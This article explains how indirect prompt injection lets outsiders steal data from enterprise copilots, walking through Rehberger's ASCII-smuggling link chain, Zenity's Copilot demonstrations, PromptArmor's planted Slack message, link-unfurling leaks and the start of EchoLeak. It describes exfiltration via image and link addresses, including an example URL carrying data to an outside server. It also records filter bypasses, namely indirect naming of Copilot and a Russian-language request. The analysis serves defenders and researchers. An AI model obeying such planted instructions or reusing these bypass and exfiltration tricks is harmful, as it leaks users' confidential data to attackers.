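# Zero-Click Data Theft from Enterprise AI Copilots in Email, Chat and Document Suites

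## How enterprise copilots read mail, chats and files

An enterprise copilot is an AI assistant that answers questions using an organisation's own mail, chats, files and records, with the access rights of the employee who asks. Microsoft 365 Copilot does this across Outlook, Teams, Word and the rest of Microsoft's office suite. Slack AI, Salesforce's Agentforce and Google's Gemini work similarly with the data in their makers' products. More than 10,000 businesses had adopted Microsoft's copilot by mid-2024, according to *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), a case study of one attack on it.

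Outsiders can write some of what a copilot reads, since anyone can email a company. From 2023 onwards, security researchers showed that an email, chat message or shared file can carry instructions that make the assistant send private data out of the organisation. In some attacks, the employee clicks nothing and never opens the attacker's message. The attacks exploit how the product normally works, so this section first follows a harmless question through Microsoft 365 Copilot.

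### One question, from the keyboard to the screen

Microsoft's documentation of Copilot's search index gives the example of an employee who wants to find an email in which a colleague praised a vendor's design work. The employee types the request, and the app passes it to the Copilot service.

The language model was not trained on the company's mail, so the service searches Microsoft Graph before passing the question to the model. Microsoft Graph is the layer through which Microsoft's services reach a customer's data. The search covers the employee's mailbox, OneDrive storage, Office files, internal SharePoint sites and Teams chat history, according to *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025), in which the security company Aim Security describes the attack.

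Copilot matches the question against this material by keyword and by meaning. To match by meaning, it uses an index that stores passages as vectors, which are long lists of numbers that are similar for passages with similar meanings. A request about praise can therefore bring back a message that contains "elated" or "amazed" but not "praise". Microsoft says new documents on shared SharePoint sites are indexed daily, while a user's mailbox is indexed in near real time, so Copilot can retrieve an email soon after it arrives.

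Copilot then adds the passages it found to the employee's question and sends the combined text to the model. This is retrieval-augmented generation (RAG), which means searching a store of documents for passages relevant to a question and adding them to the model's context before it answers. The context is all the text the model has when it produces an answer, including the question, the retrieved passages and earlier messages. Microsoft calls the retrieval step "grounding". It now calls the layer that supplies work data Work IQ, which is on by default but which licensed users can switch off with a button.

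The model's answer goes back to the Copilot service, which consults Graph and the index again for post-processing and returns the result to the app as text with formatting marks. The app, often a web page in a browser, turns those marks into headings, links and pictures. Several of the attacks send stolen data out during this step, called rendering.

### Why access rights do not keep an outsider out

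Copilot has only the permissions of the employee using it. Microsoft describes its searches as "security trimmed", meaning that they leave out anything the employee may not read, such as a restricted payroll folder. Microsoft concludes that an attacker who plants instructions in a document can reach only the data that the employee can reach.

The permission check limits a copilot to items the employee may read, but one employee's mailbox, chats and files may be exactly what a thief is after. The check also doesn't assess whether an item's author should influence the answer. A stranger's email passes because employees may read their own inboxes. Ravia notes that only people inside the organisation can put questions to Copilot, while the email in Aim's attack could come from any sender. Outside content can also arrive by routes other than email. Microsoft points out that customers can grant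 permissions to people outside the organisation, for instance through shared channels in Teams.

So a search for praise of the vendor may return both the colleague's email and a stranger's email about the same vendor. Both go into the same context, along with any confidential material the search found.

### Instructions and data in one stream

If a stranger's email contains an instruction, the model may follow it. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues, 2023) named this indirect prompt injection, in which a model follows instructions placed in content it reads rather than typed by its user. Earlier work had assumed that the attacker was the user. Greshake and colleagues demonstrated the indirect attack on Bing's GPT-4 chat and on their own test applications, and they already considered email assistants as targets.

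David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives a mild example in the December 2025 article *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. A recruiter uses a model to score each CV against the job requirements. One candidate hides an instruction in the CV to approve it for interview, and the model follows the instruction. White text on a white background would hide such a line from a human reader (Microsoft, 2025), but the attack needs no special formatting and also works in a plain text file.

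Older systems had the same problem and mostly solved it. Schneier (2024), in *LLMs’ Data-Control Path Insecurity*, gives the example of the telephone network, which once carried its control signals on the same line as callers' voices, so whistling into a handset could operate the switch. Phone companies fixed this by moving the signals to a separate channel. Databases had a similar problem with SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into, say, a web form. Programmers now write the command in advance and pass the form's contents separately (a "parameterised query"), so the database never treats those contents as a command.

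David C thinks comparing prompt injection to SQL injection is harmful because it leads people to expect a similar fix. A database engine handles commands and data differently, so programmers can keep the two separate. A language model only predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far, and nothing in that process marks some text as instructions and other text as material to read.

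Vendors try to mark the source of each text by wrapping the user's message in one kind of tag and retrieved content in another, and they train the model to obey only the former. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) tested how well the tags work by training classifiers to detect, from a model's internal activity, whose text the model was treating a passage as. Style had more influence than the tag, so models treated text that sounded like a user's request as a user's request even inside a tag for outside content. In 1,000 attempts to make an AI agent leak data, the success rate rose from 2% where this confusion was lowest to 70% where it was highest. The experiments used models and simple agents rather than a commercial copilot with its filters, so the percentages do not apply to commercial copilots, though the mechanism plausibly does.

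There is also a theoretical argument that training can never close the gap completely. Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, start from the fact that a model converts each token into the same list of numbers whether the token came from the developer's instructions or from a stranger's email. Now take one of the model's internal representations and guess whether its source was trusted. If both sources are equally likely, the lowest error rate anyone can achieve is

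$$P_e^{\star} = \tfrac{1}{2}\,(1 - \mathrm{TV})$$

where TV, the total variation distance, measures how far apart the representations of trusted and untrusted text lie. It is 1 when they do not overlap at all and 0 when they are identical. Any overlap leaves some error. For single tokens the overlap is obvious, since instructions and emails both use words like "write" and "the". For the deeper layers, where the model has blended each token with its surroundings, Pant and colleagues assume the overlap instead of proving it. That is a real gap in the argument, although the findings of Ye and colleagues suggest the assumption is a fair one. Adding that no finite training can cover every possible rewording or encoding of an input, they conclude that no safeguard inside the model can guarantee that an attacker's choice of encoding won't sway its decisions about, for example, which tools to use.

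The theorem does not estimate how often attacks succeed. It also does not cover systems in which a separate program, beyond the model's control, decides which actions to allow. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) gives the same practical advice, that the separation has to come from outside the model. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) argues that even a perfect separation may not be enough, because an agent that ignores every foreign instruction can still act on false data, for example by copying a wrong address into a tool.

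### How the data gets out

A successful injection does not by itself give the attacker anything to read. Copilot's answer appears on the employee's screen, and the attacker is elsewhere. The theft also needs an exfiltration channel, meaning any route by which data in the context reaches a server the attacker can read. (The programmer Simon Willison calls the combination of private data, an attacker's text and such a route the "lethal trifecta".)

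The simplest channel to picture is an image. Consider this address:

`images.example.org/dot.png?word=heron`

Everything after the question mark is the query string, extra information that a browser sends to the server with its request. If a web page contains an image with this address, the browser requests the picture from images.example.org as soon as it displays the page. Whoever runs that server can then find the word "heron" in its log, even if the picture doesn't exist and the person viewing the page never clicks anything.

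Chat assistants commonly write their answers in Markdown, a notation that marks formatting with ordinary punctuation. An image in Markdown is written as `![description](address)`, and an attacker can inject an instruction telling the model to put data from its context in the address. Willison describes this as a common form of exfiltration attack. Microsoft's list of channels also includes clickable links, which carry data in the same way but require a click, and tools that can publish or send data directly. Whether an assistant calls a tool can also leak one bit, if the attacker can observe it.

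Browsers offer a partial defence. A Content Security Policy (CSP) is a web page's list of the domains from which the browser may load images and other resources. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the standard, gives the example of a page that allows images only from example.com. An image from example.org would fail to load on that page, with a network error, so "heron" would never leave the browser.

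However, the policy checks only where a request is going, not the data in it. A large company's list of allowed addresses can also be long. The list Ravia published for Copilot's web page had nearly thirty distinct entries for images, some of them wildcards that allow every subdomain of sharepoint.com or teams.microsoft.com. If any server on the list will fetch an outside address on request, data can leave through it, as it did in EchoLeak. The image rule does not affect links that a person clicks. W3C recommends CSP as an additional layer of defence and advises against relying on it as the first.

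### What counts as zero-click

An attack is zero-click if it does not require the victim to click, open or approve anything, but the victim usually still does something. Reddy and Gujral say EchoLeak worked without user interaction, yet their threat model includes an employee who at least occasionally asks Copilot for something like a summary of recent emails. These statements are consistent only if "interaction" means dealing with the attacker's message.

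Some attacks run without any user action, but they need software that processes content as it arrives. Greshake and colleagues pointed to spam filters and personal assistants that read incoming mail automatically.

More often, the attacker has to wait for an employee to ask the copilot an ordinary question, such as one about a project or a company policy. The attack starts only if the search for an answer picks up the planted text. This still counts as zero-click because the employee did nothing that a careful person would avoid and may not know that the planted message exists.

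The victim has to do more when an attack depends on a question about the malicious item itself, such as a request to summarise a shared document. This kind of attack is not strictly zero-click, even when there is no link to follow, because the employee has to notice and choose the item and has usually opened it. Ravia says that earlier attacks either needed the user to point the chatbot at the malicious item in this way or were tightly limited in what data they could extract.

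Finally, a one-click attack needs the user to click a link that the attacker has prepared. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) describes its attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot as one-click.

How much the victim has to do also affects the official record of a flaw. A CVE is a public identifier for a single vulnerability, such as CVE-2025-32711 for EchoLeak. A CVSS score rates a vulnerability's severity from 0 to 10, based partly on whether the attack needs the user to take part. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* reports that Microsoft gave SearchLeak 6.5 (medium) because a user had to take part, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5 (high) because it judged that no user had to. Microsoft's reading seems better, since the attack begins with a click.

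A server-side fix is one the vendor makes on its own servers, so customers don't have to install anything. Microsoft fixed EchoLeak this way in May 2025, the month before it published the CVE.

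## Attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot before EchoLeak, 2023 to 2024

Microsoft released Microsoft 365 Copilot to enterprise customers on 1 November 2023. In the company's announcement, *Microsoft 365 Copilot is generally available*, Devine (2023) wrote that the product worked within Microsoft's existing commitments on data security and privacy. Mackie (2023) reported in *Microsoft 365 Copilot Now Generally Available* that Microsoft's main assurance was that Copilot would respect existing permissions.

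By July 2024 Microsoft's documentation also stated that Copilot blocked "prompt injections (jailbreak attacks)". It defined jailbreak attacks as user prompts designed to make a model break its rules. That definition covers an employee who types a forbidden request, but not instructions in a stranger's email, and the page did not mention indirect prompt injection. Microsoft's engineers already knew about the problem. *How to Weaponize Microsoft Copilot for Cyberattackers* (Schwartz, 2024) reports that Mark Russinovich, chief technology officer of Microsoft's Azure cloud business, presented Prompt Shields in May 2024. Developers could use this detector to look for instructions in both user prompts and retrieved text. Later versions of Microsoft's documentation list classifiers for indirect injection.

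The July 2024 page also included an assurance that prompts, retrieved data and answers stay inside the "Microsoft 365 service boundary". Two groups of researchers spent that year trying to get data across the boundary.

### Rehberger's chain

In 2023, security researcher Johann Rehberger reported to Microsoft that Bing Chat could leak data through image URLs, which were the easiest way to get data out. He recalls in *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* (2026), on his blog Embrace The Red, that Microsoft was the first vendor to acknowledge and fix the flaw. Other vendors followed, including Google, whose Bard chatbot had the same flaw.

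So when Rehberger turned to Microsoft 365 Copilot, he needed a different exfiltration channel. He chose links. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot*, which he published in August 2024, describes the attack in roughly these steps:

1. The attacker emails the victim, or shares a document, with instructions for Copilot in the text.
2. The victim asks Copilot about that item, for example for its key points.
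3. Copilot follows the instructions and searches the victim's mailbox for another message, such as one with a particular subject line.
4. Copilot writes a link to the attacker's website and adds the text of the message it found to the address, in characters the victim cannot see.
5. The victim clicks the link. The browser sends the full address to the attacker's server, and the attacker decodes it.

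Rehberger expected the injection to work, but he was surprised by the third step, in which Copilot ran the search without asking the user. This makes the attack much more useful to a thief, because the attacker can have Copilot fetch a secret that wasn't in its context when the malicious email entered it. In one demonstration, an email instructed Copilot to search for Slack login codes, and it did.

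The fourth step uses ASCII smuggling. Unicode, the standard computers use for text, includes a set of "tag" characters that mirror ASCII, the older set of English letters, digits and punctuation. Many programs do not display the tag characters. If Copilot writes "heron" in tag characters at the end of a web address, the link looks unchanged on the screen, but the browser still sends the extra characters. The model learned the encoding from one worked example in Rehberger's email.

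The invisible characters only hide the contents of the private email from the user, who might not click the link if they were visible.

This was a one-click attack. In the steps Rehberger lists, the victim first uses Copilot on the malicious item, but Rehberger pointed out that Copilot could also pick up the item through ordinary retrieval. He showed sales figures and Slack codes leaving the organisation. In principle, the attacker could ask for any email or document that Copilot could find for that user, as long as the text fitted into a link.

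### Microsoft's first response

Rehberger reported ASCII smuggling to Microsoft on 17 January 2024, and Microsoft closed the ticket the next day as low severity. That rating was defensible for the technique alone, because invisible text can't leak a secret unless something else puts the secret in it and sends it to an attacker. Rehberger replied that the severity would not be low if the technique were part of a longer attack, but Microsoft did not respond.

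On 10 February Rehberger sent Microsoft the longer attack, which demonstrated the theft of sales data from start to finish. Microsoft opened an internal case three days later. In April he told the company he meant to present the work at a conference. Microsoft asked for time until the end of May to finish a fix, and he left the attack out of his talk. In mid-May Microsoft was still working on what it called a comprehensive fix. By 2 July, a little under five months after he sent the full demonstration, Rehberger found that the attack no longer worked. Microsoft did not object to publication, and he presented the attack on 24 August. His blog post followed on 26 August, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Exposes User Data Risks*.

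It is unclear what Microsoft changed. Rehberger had recommended that Copilot stop displaying tag characters, stop running tools automatically and preferably stop showing clickable links. He noticed that links had disappeared from Copilot's answers some months before he published. He asked for details so that other vendors could learn from the fix, but he reports no answer on Embrace The Red. Prompt injection still worked. The post gives no CVE number, and its only severity rating is the "low" that Microsoft gave the hidden characters before seeing the full attack.

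### With a stolen account

Michael Bargury presented a broader set of attacks at the Black Hat security conference in Las Vegas on 8 August 2024. Bargury is a former Microsoft security architect and a co-founder of Zenity, which sells security for AI assistants, so he had a commercial reason to make the danger look large. He is nonetheless fairly open in his slides about what failed. The talk's title, *Living off Microsoft Copilot* (Bargury, 2024), adapts "living off the land", the security trade's phrase for attackers using software already present on the victim's systems.

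Zenity Labs' *Links and materials for Living off Microsoft Copilot* (2024) lists six demonstrations, three of which start after the attacker has taken over an employee's account.

Zenity released a tool called LOLCopilot for these attacks. One part asks the employee's Copilot for their closest collaborators, their documents and any emails about password resets. Another part looks up the latest exchange with each collaborator and has Copilot draft a reply in the employee's style, to which a malicious link can be added. This kind of targeted deception is called spear phishing. Bargury told TechTarget in *Zenity CTO on dangers of Microsoft Copilot prompt injections* (2024) that Zenity had made the tool "explicitly very slow" to make it hard for criminals to use at scale.

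The remaining demonstration with a stolen account bypassed sensitivity labels. When a company labels a file "confidential", a Copilot answer that cites the file inherits the label, so data loss prevention software can log or block the answer. Bargury got Copilot to reveal sensitive content without the label. He also noted that many files have no label and that Teams messages never have one.

In *Microsoft’s AI Copilot can be weaponized as an ‘automated phishing machine’*, Lazzaro (2024) makes the more serious claim that Bargury got Copilot to relay information the user had no permission to view. Zenity's own list doesn't support this. It describes bypassing data loss prevention and labelling, which control what happens to files an employee can already open. If Lazzaro meant the same demonstration, Copilot's permission check probably worked.

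Someone must break into an employee's account before these attacks can begin, so calling them zero-click would be misleading, even though the account's owner does nothing. The attacker can then read whatever Copilot can access for that employee, and needs no exfiltration channel because the answers appear on the attacker's own screen.

Microsoft's public reply fits this half of the work well. Misner, the company's head of AI incident detection and response, said that abuse of AI after a break-in resembles other things attackers do at that stage, according to Thurrott's *Security Researcher Demos Microsoft Copilot Flaws at Black Hat Conference* (2024). An attacker with the password to a mailbox could always search it, but Copilot makes the search faster and the forged emails better. Bargury's interim score in the talk listed "initial access" and "data exfil" as failures.

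### With one email from outside

The other three demonstrations do not require a compromised account, so Misner's point about break-ins does not apply to them. Zenity Labs' *Copilot Vulnerable to RCE* (2024) explains that the attacker sends the victim one email, Teams message or calendar invitation, which the victim never has to open. Teams lets people write to employees of other organisations, and Copilot read such messages even if the recipient had not accepted them. It also did not distinguish an outsider from a colleague with the same name.

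In the best-known example, an employee in accounts asks Copilot for the bank account number of a supplier they are about to pay. The correct number is in a file, but the attacker has sent an email containing a different number and instructions for Copilot to use only this text and ignore the other results. Copilot answers with the attacker's number.

Zenity also manipulated the citation, since a careful employee might check the source. Copilot marks each citation with a number, which the app turns into a link to the corresponding item in the search results. Zenity Labs' *Phantom References in Microsoft Copilot* shows that a prompt can dictate which numbers Copilot writes. In the bank example, the injected text made Copilot cite the genuine file for the false account number. Opening the file would have exposed the fraud, but the citation made checking seem unnecessary.

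The employee only asks an ordinary question, so the manipulation is zero-click. However, no data leaves the organisation, and the victim loses money only if they make the payment.

In another demonstration, Zenity made Copilot direct its user to a fake Microsoft login page. Copilot was by then suppressing web addresses in its answers, but it would still link to sources it found through web search. The injected instructions therefore made Copilot search for the attacker's site, which had to be in the index of Bing, Microsoft's search engine. The attacker gets the victim's password only if the victim asks Copilot a question, follows the link and types the password in.

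### Seventeen bits

Only one of the three outsider demonstrations took data from the company's files. Copilot could query Bing and read the results, but it could not open web pages. Zenity used the choice of query to carry information.

In the version on Bargury's slides, the victim asks Copilot for a summary of their emails. The injected instructions make Copilot check the company's files for whether Microsoft's earnings in one quarter of 2024 exceeded 53 billion dollars. Copilot then searches for an address on the attacker's site that depends on whether the answer is yes or no. It shows the result as a link and invites the victim to click it for the summary.

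Zenity Labs describes this as exfiltration "through the choice of search", but the search query goes to Bing, which the attacker doesn't run. The answer most likely reaches the attacker when the user clicks, because the site's log records which page the user visited. If so, this was also a one-click attack.

The channel was narrow, at 17 bits according to Bargury's slides. That is enough to pick out one of 131,072 possibilities ($2^{17}$), so it could answer a well-chosen question about a merger or a quarterly result, but it amounts to only about two characters of ordinary text. Rehberger's links, by contrast, could carry the body of an email. Zenity Labs' *Indirect Prompt Injection: Advanced Manipulation Techniques* notes that the web search Zenity relied on was also off by default, so a customer had to have switched it on.

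Zenity called its finding "RCE", which normally means remote code execution, in which an outsider runs programs of their choice on the victim's machine. This is among the most serious kinds of flaw. Zenity redefined the C as "Copilot" and wrote that an outsider could take "full control". Its demonstrations support the claim that one email could determine what Copilot searched for and what it wrote. But an attacker who controlled Copilot could only do what Copilot could do, and in a default installation in August 2024 that included very little that reached the outside world. Bargury argued that any plugin able to send data elsewhere would let the attacker steal it, which seems right, though the user had to choose to enable the plugin.

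Microsoft did not dispute the findings. Lazzaro reports that Misner said the company appreciated Bargury's work and was working with him on the problems. Bargury praised Microsoft's effort. His team counted ten security mechanisms inside Copilot, but as of 11 August neither these nor Prompt Shields had stopped the attack. He expected that blocking the wording he had used would help little, because he thought finding a replacement would take a few minutes on average and a few hours at most. He has an interest in that estimate, but Zenity's experience with Microsoft's filters, described below, supports it.

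### Retrieval and the missing channel

In 2024, an attacker who wanted Copilot to retrieve an email had to anticipate the user's question. The easiest to anticipate was a request to summarise recent email, which Microsoft suggested to users as a template, because a new message would be among the emails Copilot read. For more specific questions, the attacker had to guess the topic.

Zenity Labs' *Indirect Prompt Injection* shows how closely an attack document had to be tailored to Copilot and the user's question. The team's first test document worked only because the user named it in the question. For the next one, they chose a question about Japanese swords in advance and wrote the document in two parts. The upper part resembled an answer to that question, so that Copilot would retrieve it, and the lower part held the instructions. They imitated the markers that Copilot placed around each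 passage so that the model would treat the lower part as something other than retrieved text.

This worked for a harmless trick, in which Copilot printed emojis instead of an answer. When the team tried the same design on the bank details, Copilot ignored the planted text and gave the correct number from the real spreadsheet. Addressing Copilot by name in the instructions solved that, but Microsoft's filter then blocked some of the attempts. The filter stopped blocking them when the team referred to Copilot indirectly, by one of its internal functions. The team could adapt the resulting template to any question, but each document worked only when an employee asked about the subject it was written for.

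Getting the data out was harder still, because the image route had been closed since Rehberger's Bing Chat report and, by the summer of 2024, Copilot was replacing outside links with a notice that it had removed them. In Zenity Labs' *Outsmarting Copilot*, a researcher found that a request in Russian could get a working link past the link filter, hidden under the removal notice. A further test produced a link that carried text from the conversation in its address. Zenity reported the bypass on 1 July and received a reply on 14 August that it called "underwhelming".

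That result is weaker than it looks because the researcher typed the requests into Copilot directly, usually over three or more messages. Zenity suggested that an outsider's email could do the same, but only as a theoretical possibility. Even a link that got through the filter sent nothing until somebody clicked it. The attack on Slack AI that other researchers published the same month had the same limitation.

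## Slack AI and the planted public message, August 2024

Slack AI answers employees' questions from the messages in their company's workspace on Slack, a chat application owned by Salesforce. In August 2024 PromptArmor, which sells monitoring of AI products, showed that a member of a workspace could use Slack AI to steal a secret from a private channel they couldn't open.

### What Slack AI searched

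Slack divides a workspace into public channels, which any member can read, and private channels, which only invited people can read. Slack AI used retrieval-augmented generation, as Copilot does, and Slack promised customers that the tool's answers would never contain messages or files the person asking could not access.

Slack kept to that rule by searching the private channels and direct messages the person was in, plus every public channel in the workspace, including those the person had not joined or did not know existed. In a later description of its search index, Slack explains that it filters public messages by workspace membership and private ones by channel membership.

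The rule leaves the same gap as Copilot's permission check, because anyone who can post in a public channel can write text that every colleague's assistant can retrieve. The attacker can't read the victim's private channel, but the attacker's message and the victim's private messages can end up in the same context.

### The key and the placeholder

PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* gives the example of a developer who has saved an API key in a private channel with no other members. An API key is a string of characters that a program uses as a password for an online service.

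The attacker creates a public channel, stays its only member and posts one message there. The message begins with the name of the service and the words "API key", so it matches a question about the key. The rest tells the model to answer with an error notice containing a link that invites the reader to log in again. The link leads to the attacker's website, and its address contains a placeholder word that the model is supposed to replace with the other key.

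The attacker needs the placeholder because they have never seen the key. When the developer asks Slack AI for the key, both messages enter the model's context, and the model can replace the placeholder with the key. The developer then sees the error notice instead of the key. Hovering over the link would show an address ending in something like `?secret=[the key]`. If the developer clicks the link, the attacker gets the key, as in Rehberger's attack on Copilot.

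Unlike Rehberger's attack, which could also start a second search, PromptArmor's used only the search that the developer had asked for, so the planted message had to match the same question as the secret. PromptArmor wrote that the attacker does not have to know what confidential data a colleague has stored. The attacker did not know the key, but the planted message did name the service it belonged to. The developer's question also brought up other messages about API keys, and PromptArmor took this as a sign that a vaguer message might work for any secret, but did not demonstrate it. Still, naming a service is not much of an obstacle, because an employee can usually guess which ones the company uses. Willison (2024), in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection*, treats the key as just an illustration and worries more about how many chances an attacker has to plant such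 messages.

PromptArmor's second demonstration used the same kind of message for ordinary phishing. The victim asked Slack AI about the day's messages from a particular person, such as their manager, and got a link to log in again. This link carried no stolen data, so the attacker would have gained something only if the victim had followed it and then, for example, typed in a password.

### The missing citation

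Slack AI's answers include numbered citations, which Slack describes as references to the messages or files that informed the answer. In the API key example, the only citation led to the developer's own private channel, so a developer who checked it would have found their own note containing the real key. The attacker's message was not cited and did not appear on the first page of ordinary search results.

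PromptArmor did not establish why the citation was missing. Slack AI did cite the attacker's channel in the phishing demonstration, and PromptArmor called the behaviour "fairly stochastic", meaning partly random. A likely explanation is that the model selected which sources to cite as it wrote the answer. The key came from the private message, so the model could plausibly have cited that message and omitted the attacker's, which supplied the wording. Zenity's work on Copilot makes this more believable because it showed that a prompt could dictate the citation numbers, but Slack has not confirmed it.

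### A click and an account

This was a one-click attack, and the attacker also needed an account in the victim's workspace. SC Media's *Slack patches Slack AI issue that could have allowed insider phishing* stressed both conditions, and its headline fairly describes what PromptArmor had shown.

An "insider" here could be a disgruntled employee or someone using a stolen login. PromptArmor noted that companies including Disney, Uber and Twitter had already suffered leaks through Slack, and argued that the flaw "explodes the risk". That phrase is promotional, but Slack AI did increase what an insider could reach. A thief with an ordinary account could already read public channels and the private channels that account belonged to. Slack AI added a way to get at other people's private channels, if those people asked the right questions and clicked the resulting link.

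People outside the company may also have been able to carry out the attack. Slack lets two organisations share a channel, and according to its description of the search index, each organisation gets its own indexed copy of the messages. A supplier's employee could therefore write text that the customer's search covers. PromptArmor's report does not discuss shared channels, so it is unclear whether the attack would have worked from one.

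### Documents as carriers

On 14 August 2024 Slack began including uploaded files in Slack AI's answers. The change covered most file types, with exceptions such as images and spreadsheets. It was on by default, but administrators could restrict it. According to Slack's *Privacy Principles*, Slack AI's search uses uploaded files such as PDFs, emails and Word documents, as well as linked documents from Google Drive and Microsoft's SharePoint.

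This may have let an outsider without an account get instructions into the search by hiding them in a PDF that an employee then downloaded and uploaded to Slack. The instructions could then work like the planted message in the API key example. Their reach would depend on where the employee shared the PDF, because Slack gives a file the visibility of the channels it is shared in. The whole workspace could search the PDF if it was in a public channel, but only the channel's members could if it was in a private one.

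PromptArmor finished its experiments before 14 August and did not test this scenario, but called it "highly likely" based on what it had seen with messages. That inference is reasonable because the model receives text either way, but the search would still have to retrieve the document for the right question, and the victim would still have to click. Salesforce did not answer SC Media's question about malicious files.

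Slack's help page now also lists previews of shared links among the material for AI answers. When an employee posts a link to an outside website, a few words written by the site's owner can therefore enter the search. Previews are short, so an attacker has little room to work with.

### Six days in August

PromptArmor reported the flaw to Slack on 14 August, the day of the file change. Slack asked for more information on the 15th. PromptArmor sent videos and screenshots the same day and said it intended to publish. They exchanged another question and answer on the 16th.

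On 19 August Slack replied that it found the evidence insufficient. It wrote that the information PromptArmor was asking for in the first video had been posted in a public channel, and that every member can search and view public channels whether or not they have joined them. Slack called this "intended behavior."

Slack was right about its own rule, and the victim was allowed to read both messages. But PromptArmor had complained that whoever wrote one message could make the assistant send the contents of the other to a stranger's server. Willison took Slack's reply as a sign that the company did not yet understand the problem. The erratic citations may have contributed to the misunderstanding, because Slack pointed to a citation of a public channel as proof, and the citation in PromptArmor's phishing demonstration did point to one. PromptArmor was gentler than Willison and praised Slack's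 security team for responding promptly.

PromptArmor published on 20 August, six days after first reporting the problem to Slack, whereas Rehberger had waited more than six months before presenting his Copilot attack. PromptArmor said it published so soon because customers needed to know about the file change so that they could switch off the relevant settings. However, the setting it recommended only keeps files out of the search, so it would not have stopped the attack PromptArmor had demonstrated, which used a chat message.

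Soon after publication, Slack (2024) announced on 21 August that it had deployed a patch the day before, though SC Media dates the patch to the 21st. Slack said that "under very limited and specific circumstances" someone with an account in the same workspace could "phish users for certain data", and that it had no evidence of unauthorised access to customer data. A spokesperson quoted in ITPro's *Hackers could dupe Slack's AI features to expose private channel messages* similarly described using a phishing link to trick another user into sharing sensitive data.

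The limits Slack described were real, but the word "phish" understates the first demonstration. A phishing victim normally has to type in a password or hand over a file, but here Slack AI had already put the secret into the link, and the victim only had to click on what looked like a routine login problem. The lack of evidence of theft is only mildly reassuring. Slack says in its current security documentation that search answers are temporary and not stored on its servers. If that was already true in 2024, Slack could have looked for suspicious messages in public channels, but not for the answers they produced. Neither PromptArmor's report nor Slack's notice gives a CVE number or a severity score.

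Slack did not explain what it had changed. It evidently kept the search rule, because it still tells developers that a search can include any public channel in a user's workspace, even one the user has not joined. Two months after the patch, *SecAlign* (2024), a paper on training models to resist prompt injection, described the attack as one that worked on the current Slack AI, but it cited PromptArmor's demonstration for this, so it is not evidence that the patch failed.

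Slack has since described several safeguards, including filtering web addresses to prevent phishing and "context engineering" to reduce the risk of prompt injection. Slack's *Securing the Agentic Enterprise* (2025) describes filters that analyse users' queries for attacks. These would not help much against a planted message, because the victim's query is an innocent question about a key. The address filter looks more useful, because the theft depends on the link whatever the planted message says.

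### Previews that do the clicking

The attack PromptArmor described required the victim to click a link. Within a day of the publication, Rehberger pointed to a Slack feature that can make the click unnecessary when an AI system posts its answer as a message in a channel.

When a message contains a link, Slack's servers fetch the page and show a small preview under the message, a feature called unfurling. Slack does this by default for messages from people and from apps. Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* explains how this can leak data from a chatbot that posts to Slack. If injected instructions make the bot write a link with private data in the address, Slack requests that address to build the preview, and the data reaches the attacker's log before anyone clicks the link. Willison (2024), in a post with the same title, wrote that he had not thought of this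 route before.

A Content Security Policy would not block the preview request, because Slack's servers send it, not the user's browser. Developers can turn previews off with two settings on each message their app posts, one for ordinary pages and one for images and other media. They need to turn off both, because otherwise Slack has to fetch the address to find out which kind of content it is.

Rehberger was writing about apps that post messages. In PromptArmor's example, Slack AI showed its answer to the developer above the search results, and the key was sent only when the developer clicked the link, so unfurling apparently played no part.

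Rehberger found the flaw in a widely used product the following year. Anthropic had published a connector that let AI agents read and post Slack messages, built on the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting models to tools. In Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory*, a user asks Anthropic's Claude to analyse a document and post a summary for the team. Instructions in the document make Claude read the latest message in one channel and post a link containing it to a private channel. When Slack fetches the link to generate a preview, it sends the message to Rehberger's server. An administrator who had restricted the connector to posting in that private channel could reasonably have thought that nothing could leave the company.

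Rehberger reported this to Anthropic on 27 May 2025. Two days later Anthropic archived the connector, so it would get no patch. Rehberger could not tell whether his report had prompted the archiving. People were still downloading the connector more than 14,000 times a week.

This flaw did get a CVE. NIST's *CVE-2025-34072 Detail* (2025) calls it "zero-click" and shows a score of 9.3 (critical) from the security company VulnCheck, which assumed that the attack needs no action from the user. Rehberger gave it 7.5. His lower score seems more accurate, because in his example the user has to ask Claude about the malicious document, and Claude's software normally requires approval before it posts anything, unless the user has waived that step. Only the last stage, from the posted link to the attacker's server, needs no user action.

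PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* later made the same point more generally, reporting that OpenClaw, a popular AI agent, was exposed by default when used through Telegram. Slack still creates link previews by default, but its *Unfurling links in messages* now advises developers to consider turning them off for messages written by a language model.

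## How the EchoLeak attack worked

Rehberger's attack on Copilot and PromptArmor's attack on Slack AI both required the victim to click a link. In January 2025 Aim Labs, the research group at Aim Security, found an attack that needs no click, which it called EchoLeak. An outsider sends an employee one email. Later, the employee asks Microsoft 365 Copilot an ordinary question, and Copilot retrieves the email while looking for an answer. When the employee's browser displays the reply, it sends confidential text to the attacker. Aim reported the flaw (CVE-2025-32711) to Microsoft, which fixed it before Aim published the details in June.

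Aim had to get past a filter on the text Copilot reads, a filter on the links and images it writes, and the Content Security Policy of the page that shows the answer. According to Ravia, the team's first version of the attack needed the victim to click, the next needed the victim to accept an invitation, and the last needed neither.

### An email addressed to a person

Microsoft screens content for injected instructions at several layers of Copilot, using XPIA classifiers. XPIA stands for cross-prompt injection attack, Microsoft's name for indirect prompt injection. The classifiers are models trained on examples to distinguish attacks from ordinary content. If one recognises an email as an attack, the email should never reach the language model that writes the answers.

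Zenity had evaded this filter in 2024 by referring to Copilot only indirectly. Aim's email didn't mention Copilot, assistants or AI at all, and read as a set of requests to the employee who received it.

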